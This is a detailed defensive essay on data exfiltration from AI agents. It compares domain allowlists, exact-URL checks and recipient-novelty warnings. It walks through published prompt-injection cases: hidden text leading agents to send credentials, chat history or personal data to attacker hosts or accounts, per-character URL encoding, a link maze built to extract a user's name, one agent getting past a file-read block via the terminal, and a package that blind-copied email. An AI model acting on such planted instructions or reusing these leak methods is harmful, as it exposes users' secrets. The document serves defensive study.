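`webhook.site` is probably the strangest entry on a published list of approved domains. The site gives anyone a URL and shows them every request sent to it. Developers use it to test their programs, which may explain why Google put it on the default Browser URL Allowlist of Antigravity, its coding tool. In PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, a developer gives Antigravity a link to a guide for connecting some accounting software. Text in one-point type in the guide leads the agent to collect code and cloud credentials, append them to a `webhook.site` address and open that address in its browser. The request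 went through because the domain was on the allowlist.

The attack works only if Antigravity's browser tools are on, but these are one of its main features, and PromptArmor otherwise accepted the recommended settings. The agent also got around a second safeguard, a setting that barred it from reading the credentials file with its normal tool, by printing the file with a terminal command. Google had already acknowledged the risk of data exfiltration, which it warns new users about, so PromptArmor published the flaw without reporting it first. Willison (2025) covered the attack on 25 November in *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*. PromptArmor reports no fix. Deleting `webhook.site` from the default list would have stopped the attack as written, but PromptArmor says it found three other leaks that did not involve the browser tools.

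### The right host and the wrong account

Removing a domain isn't always possible. Anthropic's products can't work without `api.anthropic.com`, the address software uses to communicate with Claude, and for months attackers could steal files through that address.

The first report concerned the sandbox in which Claude runs code for users of its chat service. In October 2025 its default network setting was labelled "Package managers only", which suggests that the code can do little more than download software. The approved domains included sites from which programmers install packages, such as npm, PyPI and GitHub, but the first entry was Anthropic's own API. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* explains that this API accepts files of up to 30 megabytes each and sends them to whichever account owns the access key in the request. Rehberger planted instructions and an access key in a document. When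 a user asked Claude to summarise the document, Claude saved the user's last conversation to a file and uploaded it to Rehberger's account.

Rehberger reported the attack on 25 October. Within an hour Anthropic closed the report as out of scope, saying it was a model safety issue. Rehberger disagreed: "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries." On 30 October Anthropic accepted that such leaks fall within its reporting programme and attributed the closure to a process error, but the route stayed open.

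Anthropic released Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, in January 2026. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated the same upload in Cowork. The user had connected a folder of property documents and added a Word file of instructions found online, which contained hidden text. Cowork uploaded a loan estimate, including partial social security numbers, to the attacker's account without ever asking for approval. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a smaller model. Claude Opus 4.5, a stronger model that resists injections better, uploaded customer records by the same route in a separate test. *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (Apostol, 2026) reports that Anthropic acknowledged the risk and was preparing an update to the virtual machine in which Cowork runs code.

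In March the security company Oasis published a third version, which worked in an ordinary Claude chat with no added tools. A link can open Claude with a question already typed in, and Oasis found a way to hide further instructions in that text (Luz, 2026, *Claudy Day*). Once the user pressed Enter, Claude searched earlier conversations for sensitive material and uploaded it with the attacker's key. The attack also exploited a second check on host names, which Google uses to approve the links in its advertisements. Any address starting with `claude.com/redirect/` sent visitors on to a site chosen by the link's writer, so an attacker could buy a search advertisement that displayed a genuine `claude.com` address and led to the malicious link.

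Anthropic fixed the hidden-text flaw before Oasis published its article. In the latest version, from 27 May 2026, Oasis says work on the upload route and the redirect is still under way.

Anthropic says it fixed this in Cowork by adding a proxy inside the virtual machine. The proxy intercepts all traffic to Anthropic's API and forwards only requests that carry the session token issued to that machine, so it rejects requests that use an attacker's key. It also blocks request headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from elsewhere, which closes the relay route. The proxy has to run inside the machine because Anthropic's servers cannot distinguish a request from Cowork from one sent by any other customer's program.

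Anthropic says the incident led it to stop treating its allowlist as a filter on destinations and to regard each entry as a "capability grant", which gives the agent every function available at that domain. Approving `api.anthropic.com` so that Cowork could use Claude also allowed it to upload files to any Anthropic account.

### What identifies the recipient

On a shared service, the real destination is an account, a form or a mailbox, and the host name doesn't show who owns it. The part of the request that sent the data to the attacker varies from case to case.

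| Case | Approved domain | What led the data to the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | `asyncgw.teams.microsoft.com` | Another address, in a parameter |
| SearchLeak | `*.bing.com` | Another address, in a parameter |
| ForcedLeak | `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` | The domain itself, after it changed hands |
| Superhuman | `docs.google.com` | The form's identifier, in the path |
| Antigravity | `webhook.site` | The attacker's own URL on the site |
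| Claude file uploads | `api.anthropic.com` | The access key sent with the request |

Checking the URL in more detail would help in most of these cases, but not with the Claude uploads, where the victim and the attacker use the same URL and only the key differs. A simple proxy can usually identify the host of an encrypted request but can't read the path, parameters or key. To check those, the operator needs a proxy that decrypts the traffic, as Anthropic's does, and such a proxy is more complicated to build and handles more secrets. Anthropic notes that the widely used isolation software in its products held up well, and that the part that failed was the allowlist proxy it had written itself.

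Webhooks raise the same issue even when the company set them up on purpose. If an agent needs to post messages to a chat service, approving the service's domain approves every workspace on it, including an attacker's, because the part of the address that identifies the workspace comes after the host name.

### Traffic that never reaches the list

A list of approved domains controls only the traffic that passes through the software enforcing it, and an agent often has several ways to send a request. Superhuman's image policy had no effect on its AI's web search, which could open any URL. PromptArmor used the web search to send text from the inbox directly to an attacker's domain, without going through Google Forms. In Superhuman Go, the company's newer agent, images loaded from any domain.

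Antigravity's list had a similar gap because it governs the agent's browser but not the chat window, which loads images by itself. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) planted instructions in the title of a web page that otherwise looked empty. The agent read an access key from the computer's settings and displayed an image whose address contained the key. The chat window then requested that address from the researchers' server, which was on a domain unrelated to Google. Antigravity asked the user for permission first, but didn't name the command or the destination.

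Rules on web requests can also miss name lookups. Before a computer contacts `collector.example`, it uses the domain name system (DNS) to find the server's numerical address. If it looks up `48213.collector.example`, the query normally reaches the DNS server responsible for `collector.example`. An attacker who runs that server can read the number in its log, even if a proxy blocks the web request that was supposed to follow. Each part of a domain name can hold at most 63 characters, so a password fits into one lookup but a large file would take a great many.

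The remedy is to prevent the sandbox from making its own lookups. The proxy can make them instead, after checking the requested domain against the list.

### Repairing the list

These cases can't show how often allowlists fail, because researchers rarely publish an attack that a list stopped. They do show that the lists made these attacks harder. EchoLeak's image request failed until it went through Teams, and Noma says its leak would have been impossible without a way around Salesforce's policy. People who favour allowlists can fairly argue for maintaining them better, which is what most of the researchers who got around these lists recommend.

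The simplest fix is to approve fewer domains. Hardly any Antigravity users would miss `webhook.site`, and few companies need their agent to display images from all of `amazonaws.com`. Narrower entries also help. A policy that allowed only the part of Bing that serves images would have excluded the search-by-image feature. Rehberger suspects that other domains on Claude's "Package managers only" list could also be used to send data out. This seems likely for GitHub, where anyone can open an account and receive files.

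Shortening the list doesn't always prevent leaks, though. In EchoLeak, SearchLeak, the Bard attack and the Claude uploads, the approved domain belonged to the company that made the agent, so even a rule allowing only that company's servers would have let the data through. Large technology companies run so many services under a few domains that approving one of them can mean approving a sizeable part of the web. A short list also interferes with legitimate work. TechNadu warned Salesforce customers that agents might stop linking to documentation or feedback forms that people had forgotten to add, and OpenAI considers fixed lists too restrictive for general browsing.

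Regular audits would have caught some of these problems. Software can easily check every day whether a domain has expired. Varonis recommends that companies also look for approved domains that fetch addresses supplied by users. This takes more work, since a domain such as `bing.com` has many features, and its owner can add another without telling the companies that approved it. Auditing logs is less useful because, as Anthropic points out, the log of a successful injection shows a successful and authorised call to an approved service. Isolation can make matters worse, because the virtual machine that confined Cowork also hid its activity from the monitoring software on companies' computers. For now, Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, which it admits is not the same as watching live.

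A more complete technical fix for redirects is to have a proxy check the address at each one and stop if the next domain isn't on the list. Browsers already do this for host names under a Content Security Policy. The check works because the same machine makes every request in the sequence, so it doesn't stop a relay like Bing, whose own servers make the last request. To stop a relay, either the service must refuse such requests or the operator must block the feature that makes them.

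Account-level rules address the Claude uploads directly. In October 2025, Rehberger proposed that the sandbox should communicate only with the logged-in user's account, and Anthropic's fix for Cowork does essentially this. Anthropic could do this because it runs both the agent and the service, and already issues the token that identifies each session. A company that wants the same protection for `docs.google.com` has to work out which forms and documents belong to it and write a rule that recognises them. Other services identify the account in a subdomain, a path or a key, so each needs a different rule. If a service identifies accounts by URL, the company ends up approving individual addresses.

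## Approving only exact addresses that were already known

An exact-URL check approves only addresses that were known before the conversation began, since those cannot have been built from the secrets in it. It would refuse the request that carries Ana's card number, because nobody had a reason to publish that address beforehand. Nobody would have to work out who owns `collector.example`.

Approving only exact addresses that were already known would have stopped most of the attacks that got past domain allowlists. EchoLeak's request went to a Teams server, SearchLeak's to Bing and Superhuman's to Google Forms. All three were on approved domains, but each address was new because it contained text from the victim's mail or files. The same is true of the leaks through Salesforce's expired domain and through `webhook.site`. The Claude file uploads would still have worked, because the agent sent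 the stolen data in the body of a request to an address that every Claude developer uses.

Redirects also matter less here than with a list of domains. An address that asks a reputable site to forward the agent to `collector.example/48213` contains the number, so it fails like any other new address. A known address may still forward the agent to the attacker's server. But whoever wrote the redirect didn't have Ana's number and couldn't put it in the next address. (A site where Ana is logged in is an exception, since it may already know things about her.)

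### Two meanings of "known"

OpenAI compares the address with a public URL index. In the January 2026 post that introduced the check, Spânu and Shadwell cite redirects as one reason for not using a list of trusted sites instead. The other reason is that people visit far more than a handful of popular sites, so a strict list would produce frequent warnings and could train people to click through them.

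The index comes from a crawler that scans public pages much as a search engine does and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the address matches an entry, the agent can open the article or load the image automatically. If it doesn't, OpenAI either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. The warning displays the address, and the user can copy it or open it anyway.

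OpenAI published the technical details in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. Rehberger, who reviewed the paper on Embrace The Red, had guessed in 2023 that ChatGPT might be checking Bing's index, but OpenAI uses its own. As he understands the system, an address the user enters in a message also counts as safe for the rest of that chat.

Anthropic's `web_fetch` tool, which lets Claude read web pages and PDFs, needs no crawler. It became available to developers in September 2025. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, Claude may not construct addresses and can fetch only those that have already appeared in the conversation, whether in a user message, the output of a tool the developer runs, or the results of an earlier search or fetch. The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. Google applies a similar check in Chrome to addresses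 that its agent's model writes.

The two versions differ in where an address can come from. An address in OpenAI's index was public independently of Ana's chat, whereas one in Claude's conversation may have just arrived in the attacker's email. Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, pointed this out on the day `web_fetch` came out. Developers often paste outside text into what the software counts as a user message. For example, a program that summarises incoming mail might put each email there, and every link in the email would then count as one the user had supplied. Willison still thought the ban on addresses written by Claude gave the most protection, because the usual attack tells the model to attach private data to the attacker's address. He also tried the tool in the consumer Claude app and found the same restriction.

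Tool output creates a less obvious gap. If a developer gives Claude a tool that runs code and returns whatever the code prints, Claude could write code that prints `collector.example/48213`. By default, `web_fetch` would then accept that address because it appeared in a tool result, even though Claude wrote it. Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, a newer Chinese edition of the same guide, describes this problem and a setting, `url_sources`, that lets developers exclude a particular tool or a whole class of sources. It also says that `web_fetch` refuses an address that seems to contain a password or access key, unless that credential also appears in the developer's instructions or in the text of a user message.

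Anthropic chose stricter defaults for Managed Agents, its service for running developers' agents. According to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026), since 7 October 2026 `web_fetch` in Managed Agents has accepted only addresses that have already appeared in the session. Addresses in attached documents, or in the output of tools that run commands or read files, do not count. Links on pages the agent has already fetched do count, which matters for an attack described below.

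### How OpenAI arrived at a public index

Before adopting this design, OpenAI used a check called `url_safe`, which appeared in ChatGPT's web app in December 2023. Before displaying an image, the app sent the image's address to OpenAI's server, which replied that it was safe or unsafe. OpenAI did not publish the criteria, and Rehberger couldn't work them out. He reported on Embrace The Red that he made 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them loaded, including the one for "a" but not the one for "d". Those nine were enough to leak the word "hi" with two requests. Rehberger suggested limiting the number of images in an answer and moving the check to the server, so that every app would get it.

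Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* found that ChatGPT's browsing tool accepted any bare domain but generally refused subdomains, probably because an attacker can put data in them. As exceptions, it accepted any subdomain of `google.com` and any subdomain, path and parameters under `openai.com`. Imperva leaked data without these exceptions by preparing a separate fixed address for each character.

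*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) describes a similar attack. ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt at the time, so the researchers could steal ten characters per prompt. Opening many pages was also slow, which gave the user a chance to notice and stop the attack. The researchers expected a "cat and mouse game" for as long as ChatGPT could open arbitrary addresses.

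Attackers who wanted to steal more than a few characters could use hosts on which `url_safe` allowed every address. One was `windows.net`, where Microsoft's cloud customers store files. Anyone can open a storage account there and read the log of requests to it. In Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, Rehberger planted instructions in a PDF. When a user asked ChatGPT about the document, ChatGPT copied its notes on the user's recent conversations into an image address on Rehberger's storage account. He had reported the problem in October 2024, along with a second host, `apache.org`, whose logs he could also read. OpenAI had not fixed the problem when he published. Tenable (2025) found that `url_safe` always allowed addresses on `bing.com` and used this to get past the check. At this stage, OpenAI's check had the same weakness as other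 companies' domain allowlists. According to Rehberger, changes around August 2025 stopped the attacks he had demonstrated.

The check also covered only what ChatGPT displayed. The Deep Research feature opened pages from OpenAI's servers, and Radware's *ShadowLeak* found no comparable limit on the addresses it could visit. Radware's researchers sent an email that looked like a follow-up on staff changes. When the user asked for a report on the day's emails, Deep Research took an employee's name and home address from another message and sent them to the researchers' server. The transfer did not appear on the user's screen or pass through the user's computer or office network.

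Radware needed several attempts to make the attack work. The model identified direct requests to send personal data as malicious. When it treated an address as suspicious, it sometimes searched for the address online instead of opening it. Later versions of the email got it to open the page, but it did not always attach the data. The version that worked told the agent to encode the data in base64 first, supposedly for security. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests. OpenAI later published the first part of what seems to be the same email as an example of a realistic attack, and gives a 50% success rate for the same user request. Radware had several working variants, so the two figures may describe different ones, but either rate is high enough to be useful to an attacker. Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August and acknowledged it on 3 September.

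OpenAI then limited ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as it had received them, and it refused to add parameters even when told to. This was similar to Anthropic's rule for `web_fetch` and had the same weakness, since an attacker can supply ready-made addresses. Radware's *ZombieAgent* did this with an email listing one address for each letter and digit, plus one for spaces. The agent found the private text and spelled it out by opening the matching addresses without changing them.

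OpenAI had also tried to keep such attacks from lasting beyond a single chat by preventing ChatGPT from opening an attacker's address stored in its memory, the notes it keeps about a user between chats. Radware left the addresses in the email and stored in memory only an instruction to read that email before each reply. ChatGPT then got the addresses from the email every time, which the rules allowed, and the leak continued in new chats.

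Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, the fix lets ChatGPT open links from emails only under certain conditions, such as when the link appears in a well-known public index. An attacker's newly made pages, one for each letter, would not normally be in such an index.

By March 2026 OpenAI was calling the protection Safe Url. It covers ChatGPT's own requests, searches and page visits in Deep Research, and page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser. A sandbox gives similar protection for small programs that ChatGPT builds in Canvas or runs as apps, and prompts the user before allowing unexpected communication. OpenAI says the model refuses most attacks it knows of before these protections are needed.

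Rehberger still worries that some developers at a large company won't know a good check exists, and so may build products without it. PromptArmor's attack on Codex, reported three months after OpenAI's post, suggests he was right. The image address in that attack contained the user's emails, so it could not have been in a public index, and Codex presumably did not apply the check.

### Spelling a secret with public pages

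Even when the check works perfectly, an attacker can use the method Rehberger described in 2023, in which each of 36 harmless pages stands for one letter or digit. The pages only have to be in the index, so an ordinary blog with 36 articles is enough. OpenAI acknowledges this leak in its paper.

The amount of information that leaks depends on how many different messages the attacker's server can distinguish. If it can distinguish *M* messages, it receives at most log₂ *M* bits, which is about 5.17 bits for one choice among 36 pages. For five visits, *M* depends on whether the agent can open a page twice and whether the server can detect the order of the visits.

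| What the attacker's server sees | Possible messages | Bits |
|---|---|---|
| Five visits in order, repeats allowed | 36⁵ = 60,466,176 | 25.85 |
| Five visits in order, no page twice | 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 × 32 = 45,239,040 | 25.43 |
| Five different pages, order lost | 45,239,040 ÷ 120 = 376,992 | 18.5 |

The last row is divided by 120 because five different pages can be arranged in 120 ways (5 × 4 × 3 × 2 × 1). If Ana's agent spells out 48213 and the requests arrive scrambled, the attacker knows which digits the number contains and has 120 arrangements to try. A website that locks an account after a few wrong guesses would stop most of those attempts, but many systems that accept a loyalty number would not.

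A more careful attacker wouldn't need to guess. There are only 100,000 five-digit numbers (about 16.6 bits), and even the last row allows 376,992 messages, so the attacker could assign a different set of five pages to every possible card number. This would be awkward for a model to do without running code, but easy for an agent that can run it.

### Caching and repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two ways to make this harder. The agent's software could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and use it if the agent asks for the page again, or it could refuse to visit the same address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker receives at most one request for each page.

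Banning repeat visits to a page barely reduces how much data an attacker can send. By the arithmetic above, five visits can carry 25.43 bits instead of 25.85. The ban disrupts the simple one-page-per-character code more, because the second "l" in "hello" never arrives. About a quarter of random five-character codes contain a repeated character, as do about 87% of random twelve-character passwords, so an attacker using the simple code would often receive a secret with characters missing.

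But the attacker can change the code to use a separate address for each character in each position, as Radware had already done in ZombieAgent to keep the letters in sequence. The letter "a" in the first position then has a different address from "a" in the second. Five characters require 36 × 5 = 180 pages. The agent never needs to open a page twice, and the requests can arrive in any order because each page corresponds to a specific position. The attacker gets the full 25.85 bits back. Ana's card number, which contains only digits, would require just 50 pages.

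A larger set of pages has a similar effect. Rehberger notes that an attacker could go from 36 addresses to thousands. With 1,000 pages, one visit carries almost 10 bits, and visits to five different pages in unknown order carry about 42.9 bits, much more than five unrestricted visits to a set of 36 pages. With 100,000 indexed pages, one for every five-digit number, a single visit would reveal Ana's whole card number. One of those addresses could end in `48213`, and it would have been public before the conversation, like the other 99,999.

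Caching and a ban on repeat visits are easy to add and inconvenience an unprepared attacker, but they also interfere with legitimate tasks such as watching a ticket price, which requires loading the same page again. `web_fetch` caches pages by default, but developers can turn this off to get current content.

Limiting the number of visits has a more predictable effect. At most *k* visits among *n* pages can carry no more than about *k* × log₂ *n* bits, plus a little for the number of visits. With 36 pages, the ten-address limit that ChatGPT had in 2024 would allow about 52 bits, enough for a random ten-character password of lowercase letters and digits. Anthropic lets developers set a limit for `web_fetch` but does not impose one by default.

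The exact-URL check still limits what an attacker can practically steal. Superhuman's AI leaked the full text of several emails in one answer. Using 36 pages to spell out a single 2,000-character email would take 2,000 visits, one per character, which would be slow and conspicuous in any log. Names, login codes and passwords are short enough to steal this way. Lockdown Mode prevents even this leak by serving only stored copies of pages. A stored page can still carry an injection to the model, according to a passage from *OpenAI Help* quoted by Willison (2026).

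### Links created during the conversation

The attacks on public pages require some preparation, because the attacker's addresses must first get into the index. Under Anthropic's rule, the attacker's server could instead create addresses while the agent was working. Ayush Paul demonstrated this against the ordinary Claude chat app in July 2026. The app is an attractive target because it can remember facts about the user from earlier conversations.

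Paul built a website for an imaginary coffee shop that looked normal to ordinary visitors but showed Claude a different page. That page claimed that an AI assistant had to identify its user before it could continue. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) explains how the page worked around the limits of `web_fetch`. Claude could not write an address containing the user's name, but it could follow links on a page it had already fetched. Paul therefore gave it an alphabetical directory of user profiles and asked it to find the right one letter by letter. Paul obtained the user's name, employer and home city this way.

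The user had never told Claude their home city. According to dyb's blog post about the attack, *The Read-Only Lie*, Claude inferred it from the name of a school hackathon. Deleting the user's address from Claude's memory would not have kept the city private.

Each page offered 27 links, one for every letter and one for a hyphen, so each choice carried log₂ 27, or about 4.75 bits. The blog post estimates that the attack took about 30 choices, or roughly 143 bits. Neither of Rehberger's proposals would have reduced this, because every address was one character longer than the last. On a site like this, Claude would spell out Ana's number by following links to `/4`, `/48`, `/482`, `/4821` and `/48213`, without repeating an address, and the last address would contain the whole number in order.

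Claude did not write any of these addresses, so it obeyed the rule. But the server created the later ones in response to Claude's choices, and the final address effectively did not exist before the conversation. Checking addresses against a public index would make this particular design harder to use, because the attacker would need 111,110 indexed pages to cover every path through a five-digit number, compared with 50 using Radware's method. The number of paths grows much faster for names and passwords.

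Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and paid no reward for the report. It fixed the chat app by preventing `web_fetch` from following links that appear only in pages it has fetched. Claude can still open addresses that the user enters or that a web search returns.

The rules for developers are looser. In Anthropic's newer guide, links in fetched pages are still an accepted source by default, and the October rule for Managed Agents explicitly includes them. An agent built on either could in principle be tricked by a site like Paul's if it has private data. Developers using the ordinary API can switch this source off with the `url_sources` setting. Anthropic also warns developers not to use `web_fetch` where Claude handles sensitive data together with untrusted text. It probably keeps the default because agents need to follow links to read documentation or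 long articles split over several pages, and many developers' agents handle no secrets.

The blog post suggests a compromise in which the agent follows links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. This would stop a random search result from leading the agent through a maze of links. It would be less effective against Paul's site, since a user might well ask Claude about a coffee shop by name.

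### What remains outside the guarantee

OpenAI states a narrow guarantee for the check, which is meant to prevent an agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it fetches something. "Quietly" matters because the user can accept the warning and send the data anyway. The check also doesn't establish that a page is honest or free of hidden instructions. An agent might load an indexed page and follow instructions on it to email Ana's card number to someone, even though the exact-URL check worked as designed.

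Visiting an address also reveals something even when the address contains no secret. For instance, the images in the leak that Permiso found in ChatGPT could have had ordinary public addresses that were the same for every visitor.

The exception for addresses that users enter is reasonable because a person who types an address normally wants the agent to open it. Pasted text is riskier. A web page that tampers with copied text, like Samoilenko's in 2023, could add 36 ready-made addresses, and software that treats everything in the message box as the user's own words would accept them all. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* suggested refusing to open any link when a prompt contains pasted text. That would be safe, but it would block the most common way to ask an agent about a page, which is to paste a link.

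The check causes problems for legitimate pages that nobody has indexed. A news article may be too recent for the crawler to have found, a company's internal pages are closed to crawlers, and a link to a shared document may be deliberately secret. Anthropic's rule is more convenient for these pages because Claude will open an address that the user pastes. OpenAI apparently allows this too, but an unindexed link that the agent finds itself leads to a warning or a search for another source. OpenAI's post doesn't include figures for how often this happens, so it is hard to say whether the index causes fewer interruptions than the lists of trusted sites that OpenAI rejected.

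Personalised pages are the hardest case. To compare hotel prices, Ana's agent may need an address like this one:

`hotel.example/rooms?arrive=2026-12-20&nights=3&card=48213`

The address is new, and it contains private data from the conversation. It is also what Ana wants, because the hotel gives a discount to loyalty-card holders. An index can't contain this address, and `web_fetch` wouldn't accept it if Claude wrote it. It fails the test of prior existence, as does the request to `collector.example`. The two requests differ in who receives the number, so the software has to ask Ana or look for other evidence about the hotel's site.

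## Treating first-time recipients and unfamiliar sites as warnings

An agent can use past dealings with a site as one piece of evidence about whether a request is legitimate. If Ana books at `hotel.example` every year, a request to send it her card number is probably what she wants. The same request for `collector.example`, which nobody at her company has ever contacted, deserves more suspicion, though it could still be legitimate. The agent should check unfamiliar destinations more closely rather than block them automatically, because an agent limited to sites and people its user already knew could not compare hotels in a new city or write to a new customer.

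An unfamiliar destination can be a warning because a hijacked agent often sends data to a place the attacker controls, where the user has rarely had a reason to go. Google (2026) argues more generally that attacks often push a browser agent outside its normal statistical range, so it advises developers to look for unusual behaviour with both live alerts and later analysis.

Bayes' rule shows how much a new destination should raise suspicion:

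`odds of theft after = odds of theft before × (share of thefts that go to new destinations ÷ share of honest actions that do)`

Suppose, using invented numbers, that one action in 10,000 is a theft, and that 90% of thefts but only 5% of honest actions go to new destinations. A new destination then multiplies the odds of theft by 18 (90% divided by 5%). But only about one flagged action in 556 is a theft, so a ban on new destinations would block about 555 honest actions for each theft it prevented. If honest actions went to new destinations as often as thefts do, the ratio would be 1 and a new destination would not be evidence of theft.

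### Four meanings of "new"

A destination can be new to the user, the organisation, the task or the web. Suppose Ana asks her agent to plan a work trip and it tries to contact four sites.

| Site | New to Ana? | New to her employer? | New to the task? | New to the web? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `guesthouse.example`, which Ana asked about and which opened last month | Yes | Yes | No | Yes |
| `rail.example`, where her colleagues buy train tickets | Yes | No | No | No |
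| `payroll.example`, where Ana reads her payslips | No | No | Yes | No |
| `collector.example`, a ten-year-old domain that the attacker bought from its previous owner | Yes | Yes | Yes | No |

A warning based on Ana's own history flags the guesthouse and the railway as well as the attacker. One based on her employer's history clears the railway. One based on the registration date gets the two most important cases wrong, since it flags the guesthouse and clears the attacker.

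Only the comparison with the task flags the payroll site, which Ana uses every month but a trip-planning agent has no reason to open. This comparison gives the right answer in all four rows, but it is the hardest to automate. Software can make the other three comparisons by checking a log or a public register, while another model usually has to judge whether a site fits the task.

A site that is new to the whole company is also new to Ana at work, so a system that counted both facts as independent warnings would overestimate the risk.

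### Warnings about email recipients

Email programs have warned people about unfamiliar addresses for years. Google's *Unintended external reply warnings in Gmail to mitigate unintentional data loss* (2017) introduced such a warning for business users. When a user replies to a message, Gmail checks the recipients, including those copied in, and warns about outside addresses that are not in the user's contacts or that the user doesn't write to regularly. If the user dismisses the warning, Gmail never shows it again for that address.

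Google's *Email threads with recipients outside your organization will be labeled “External”* (2021) announced a label that appears on any conversation with someone outside the organisation, regardless of past contact. Administrators can turn it off. Later that year, Google (2021) changed the window where people write messages. Gmail now highlights an outside contact there in deep yellow if the user has interacted with them before, and adds a warning banner if not. The University of Michigan's *Coming soon*, a notice to staff and students, explains that these marks also apply to the blind-copy field.

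Microsoft's *MailTips in Exchange Online* describes a simpler warning, which tells senders that a message will leave the organisation. The warning is the same for a supplier of ten years and a complete stranger, and it is off until an administrator turns it on. *Why am I seeing an alert in Outlook* adds that the warning is for information only, so dismissing it does not remove any recipients.

Microsoft's "first contact safety tip" warns people when they get a message from an address that has never or rarely written to them. Microsoft recommends turning it on to protect against impersonation. The tip could also help with prompt injection, because it flags when a stranger's text enters the mailbox, but it doesn't check where the agent later sends data.

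On their own, these warnings would not slow down an agent that sends mail through an API, because they appear in a window that the agent never opens, where a person is writing or reading. Outlook requests its notices from the mail server. An agent's developer would have to request the same information and then decide what the agent should do with it, such as hold the message until the user has seen the address.

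### What research on misdirected email found

Researchers have tested whether software can use past mail to detect a wrong recipient. They were studying human mistakes, such as accepting the wrong autocomplete suggestion for an email address.

Carvalho and Cohen (2007) used the mail of 20 Enron employees in *Preventing Information Leaks in Email*. A US regulator had published the energy company's messages during its fraud investigation. They trained their program on the oldest 90% of each person's sent mail and on the mail the person had received. They then added one wrong recipient from the person's address book to each of the newer sent messages, usually one whose address began like a real recipient's, and tested whether the program could identify the added recipient.

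Random guessing found the wrong recipient 41% of the time. Comparing the message with earlier mail to each person raised this to 56%. Adding how often the sender had exchanged mail with each recipient raised it to 80%, and the best version reached 81%. The record of past contact accounted for most of the improvement, even though every wrong recipient was already in the address book.

Carvalho and Cohen then searched the Enron mail for apologies and found two real leaks they could test. One message had 20 recipients and the other had 44. In 100 attempts on each message, the program never identified the wrong address. Both leaks went to people who did not appear in the sender's earlier mail, whereas the artificial mistakes used for training all involved known contacts.

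The researchers retrained the program with a fifth of the artificial mistakes sent to unknown addresses. The retrained program found the first leak in about 90% of attempts but the second in only 25%. The second message had four unknown recipients, three of them correct, and the sender's history contained nothing to distinguish the wrong one. The retraining also reduced the score on the original test from 81% to 76%.

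Zilberman, Shabtai and Rokach found the same limit on a larger scale in *Analyzing Group Communication for Preventing Data Leakage via Email*, using 17 Enron mail folders. Their first program considered only earlier mail between the sender and each recipient, so it flagged every recipient who was new to the sender, whether wrong or correct.

Their second program sorted employees into groups that discussed the same topics. It accepted a new recipient if the sender and recipient shared a group and the message resembled that group's mail. At the setting the researchers highlight, it flagged 51% of the wrong new recipients and 40% of the correct ones. By the formula above, a flag multiplies the odds of a mistake by less than 1.3. Flagging 40% of new recipients at random would have caught 40% of the wrong ones, so the topic groups added little.

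People seem to find such software useful anyway. Zilberman and colleagues summarise a trial of a version of Carvalho's program in Thunderbird, an email application. More than 15% of participants reported that it had prevented a real leak, and more than 80% said they would keep using it if the developers made a few improvements. The 2007 experiments can't show how many needless warnings the program would produce, because Carvalho and Cohen tested it only on messages that contained a mistake.

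These methods transfer only partly to agents. They work best when a message has several recipients and one doesn't fit with the others, but a hijacked agent can send its email to a single address. Zilberman and colleagues point out the same weakness in a Google feature called "Got the Wrong Bob", which worked only on group emails. But an agent's software has the user's request, which the Enron researchers lacked. If Ana asks her agent to send the itinerary to her sister and it addresses the message to a stranger, a check doesn't need to infer her intention from old mail.

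### Blind copies and forwarding rules

An email's visible recipient may be the one the user asked for while a second copy goes elsewhere. This happened with `postmark-mcp`, a code package on npm that connected AI agents to Postmark, a service companies use to send email from their software. The package used the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for giving tools to models.

Koi, the security company that discovered the problem, reports that the first 15 versions worked properly. In version 1.0.16, the publisher added one line of code that blind-copied every message to an address at `giftshop.club`. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of software flaws, confirms the version and the method. Postmark says it was not involved with the package and had not published its own MCP tool on npm.

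This theft needed no prompt injection. The agent asked its tool to email a customer, and the tool did so. A check on the agent's request would have found only the customer's address, but a check at the mail service, after the tool had assembled the message, could have found `giftshop.club`. That domain must have been new to nearly everyone affected.

If the system learned from all outgoing mail, that warning would have stopped within a day or so, because the attacker's address would have looked like the user's most regular contact. The address appeared alongside every other recipient, which would even have made it look safer on one of Carvalho and Cohen's measures, since that measure is based on the assumption that a wrong recipient seldom appears with the others. It would be safer for the system to learn only from recipients that a person chose or approved. A single address that suddenly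 appears on every message should also trigger a separate warning.

Koi guesses that between 3,000 and 15,000 emails a day went to the attacker. It assumes that 20% of the 1,500 weekly downloads represent organisations actively using the tool, and that each sends 10 to 50 emails a day. The true figure may be much lower. The Hacker News (2025) reports 1,643 downloads in total and says the developer uploaded the package on 15 September 2025, only 11 days before the database entry. Koi, which sells software for detecting such changes, describes a tool that people had relied on for much longer. After Koi contacted the developer, he deleted the package from npm without replying, but versions already installed could still send the blind copies.

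Forwarding rules create a similar gap. A user, or an agent with access to the mail settings, can tell the mail service to send a copy of all future mail to another address. The service then sends the copies itself, so a check on the agent's outgoing messages misses them. The check has to run when the agent creates or changes the rule. A new outside address in a forwarding rule deserves more concern than one in a single email because it will receive all later mail.

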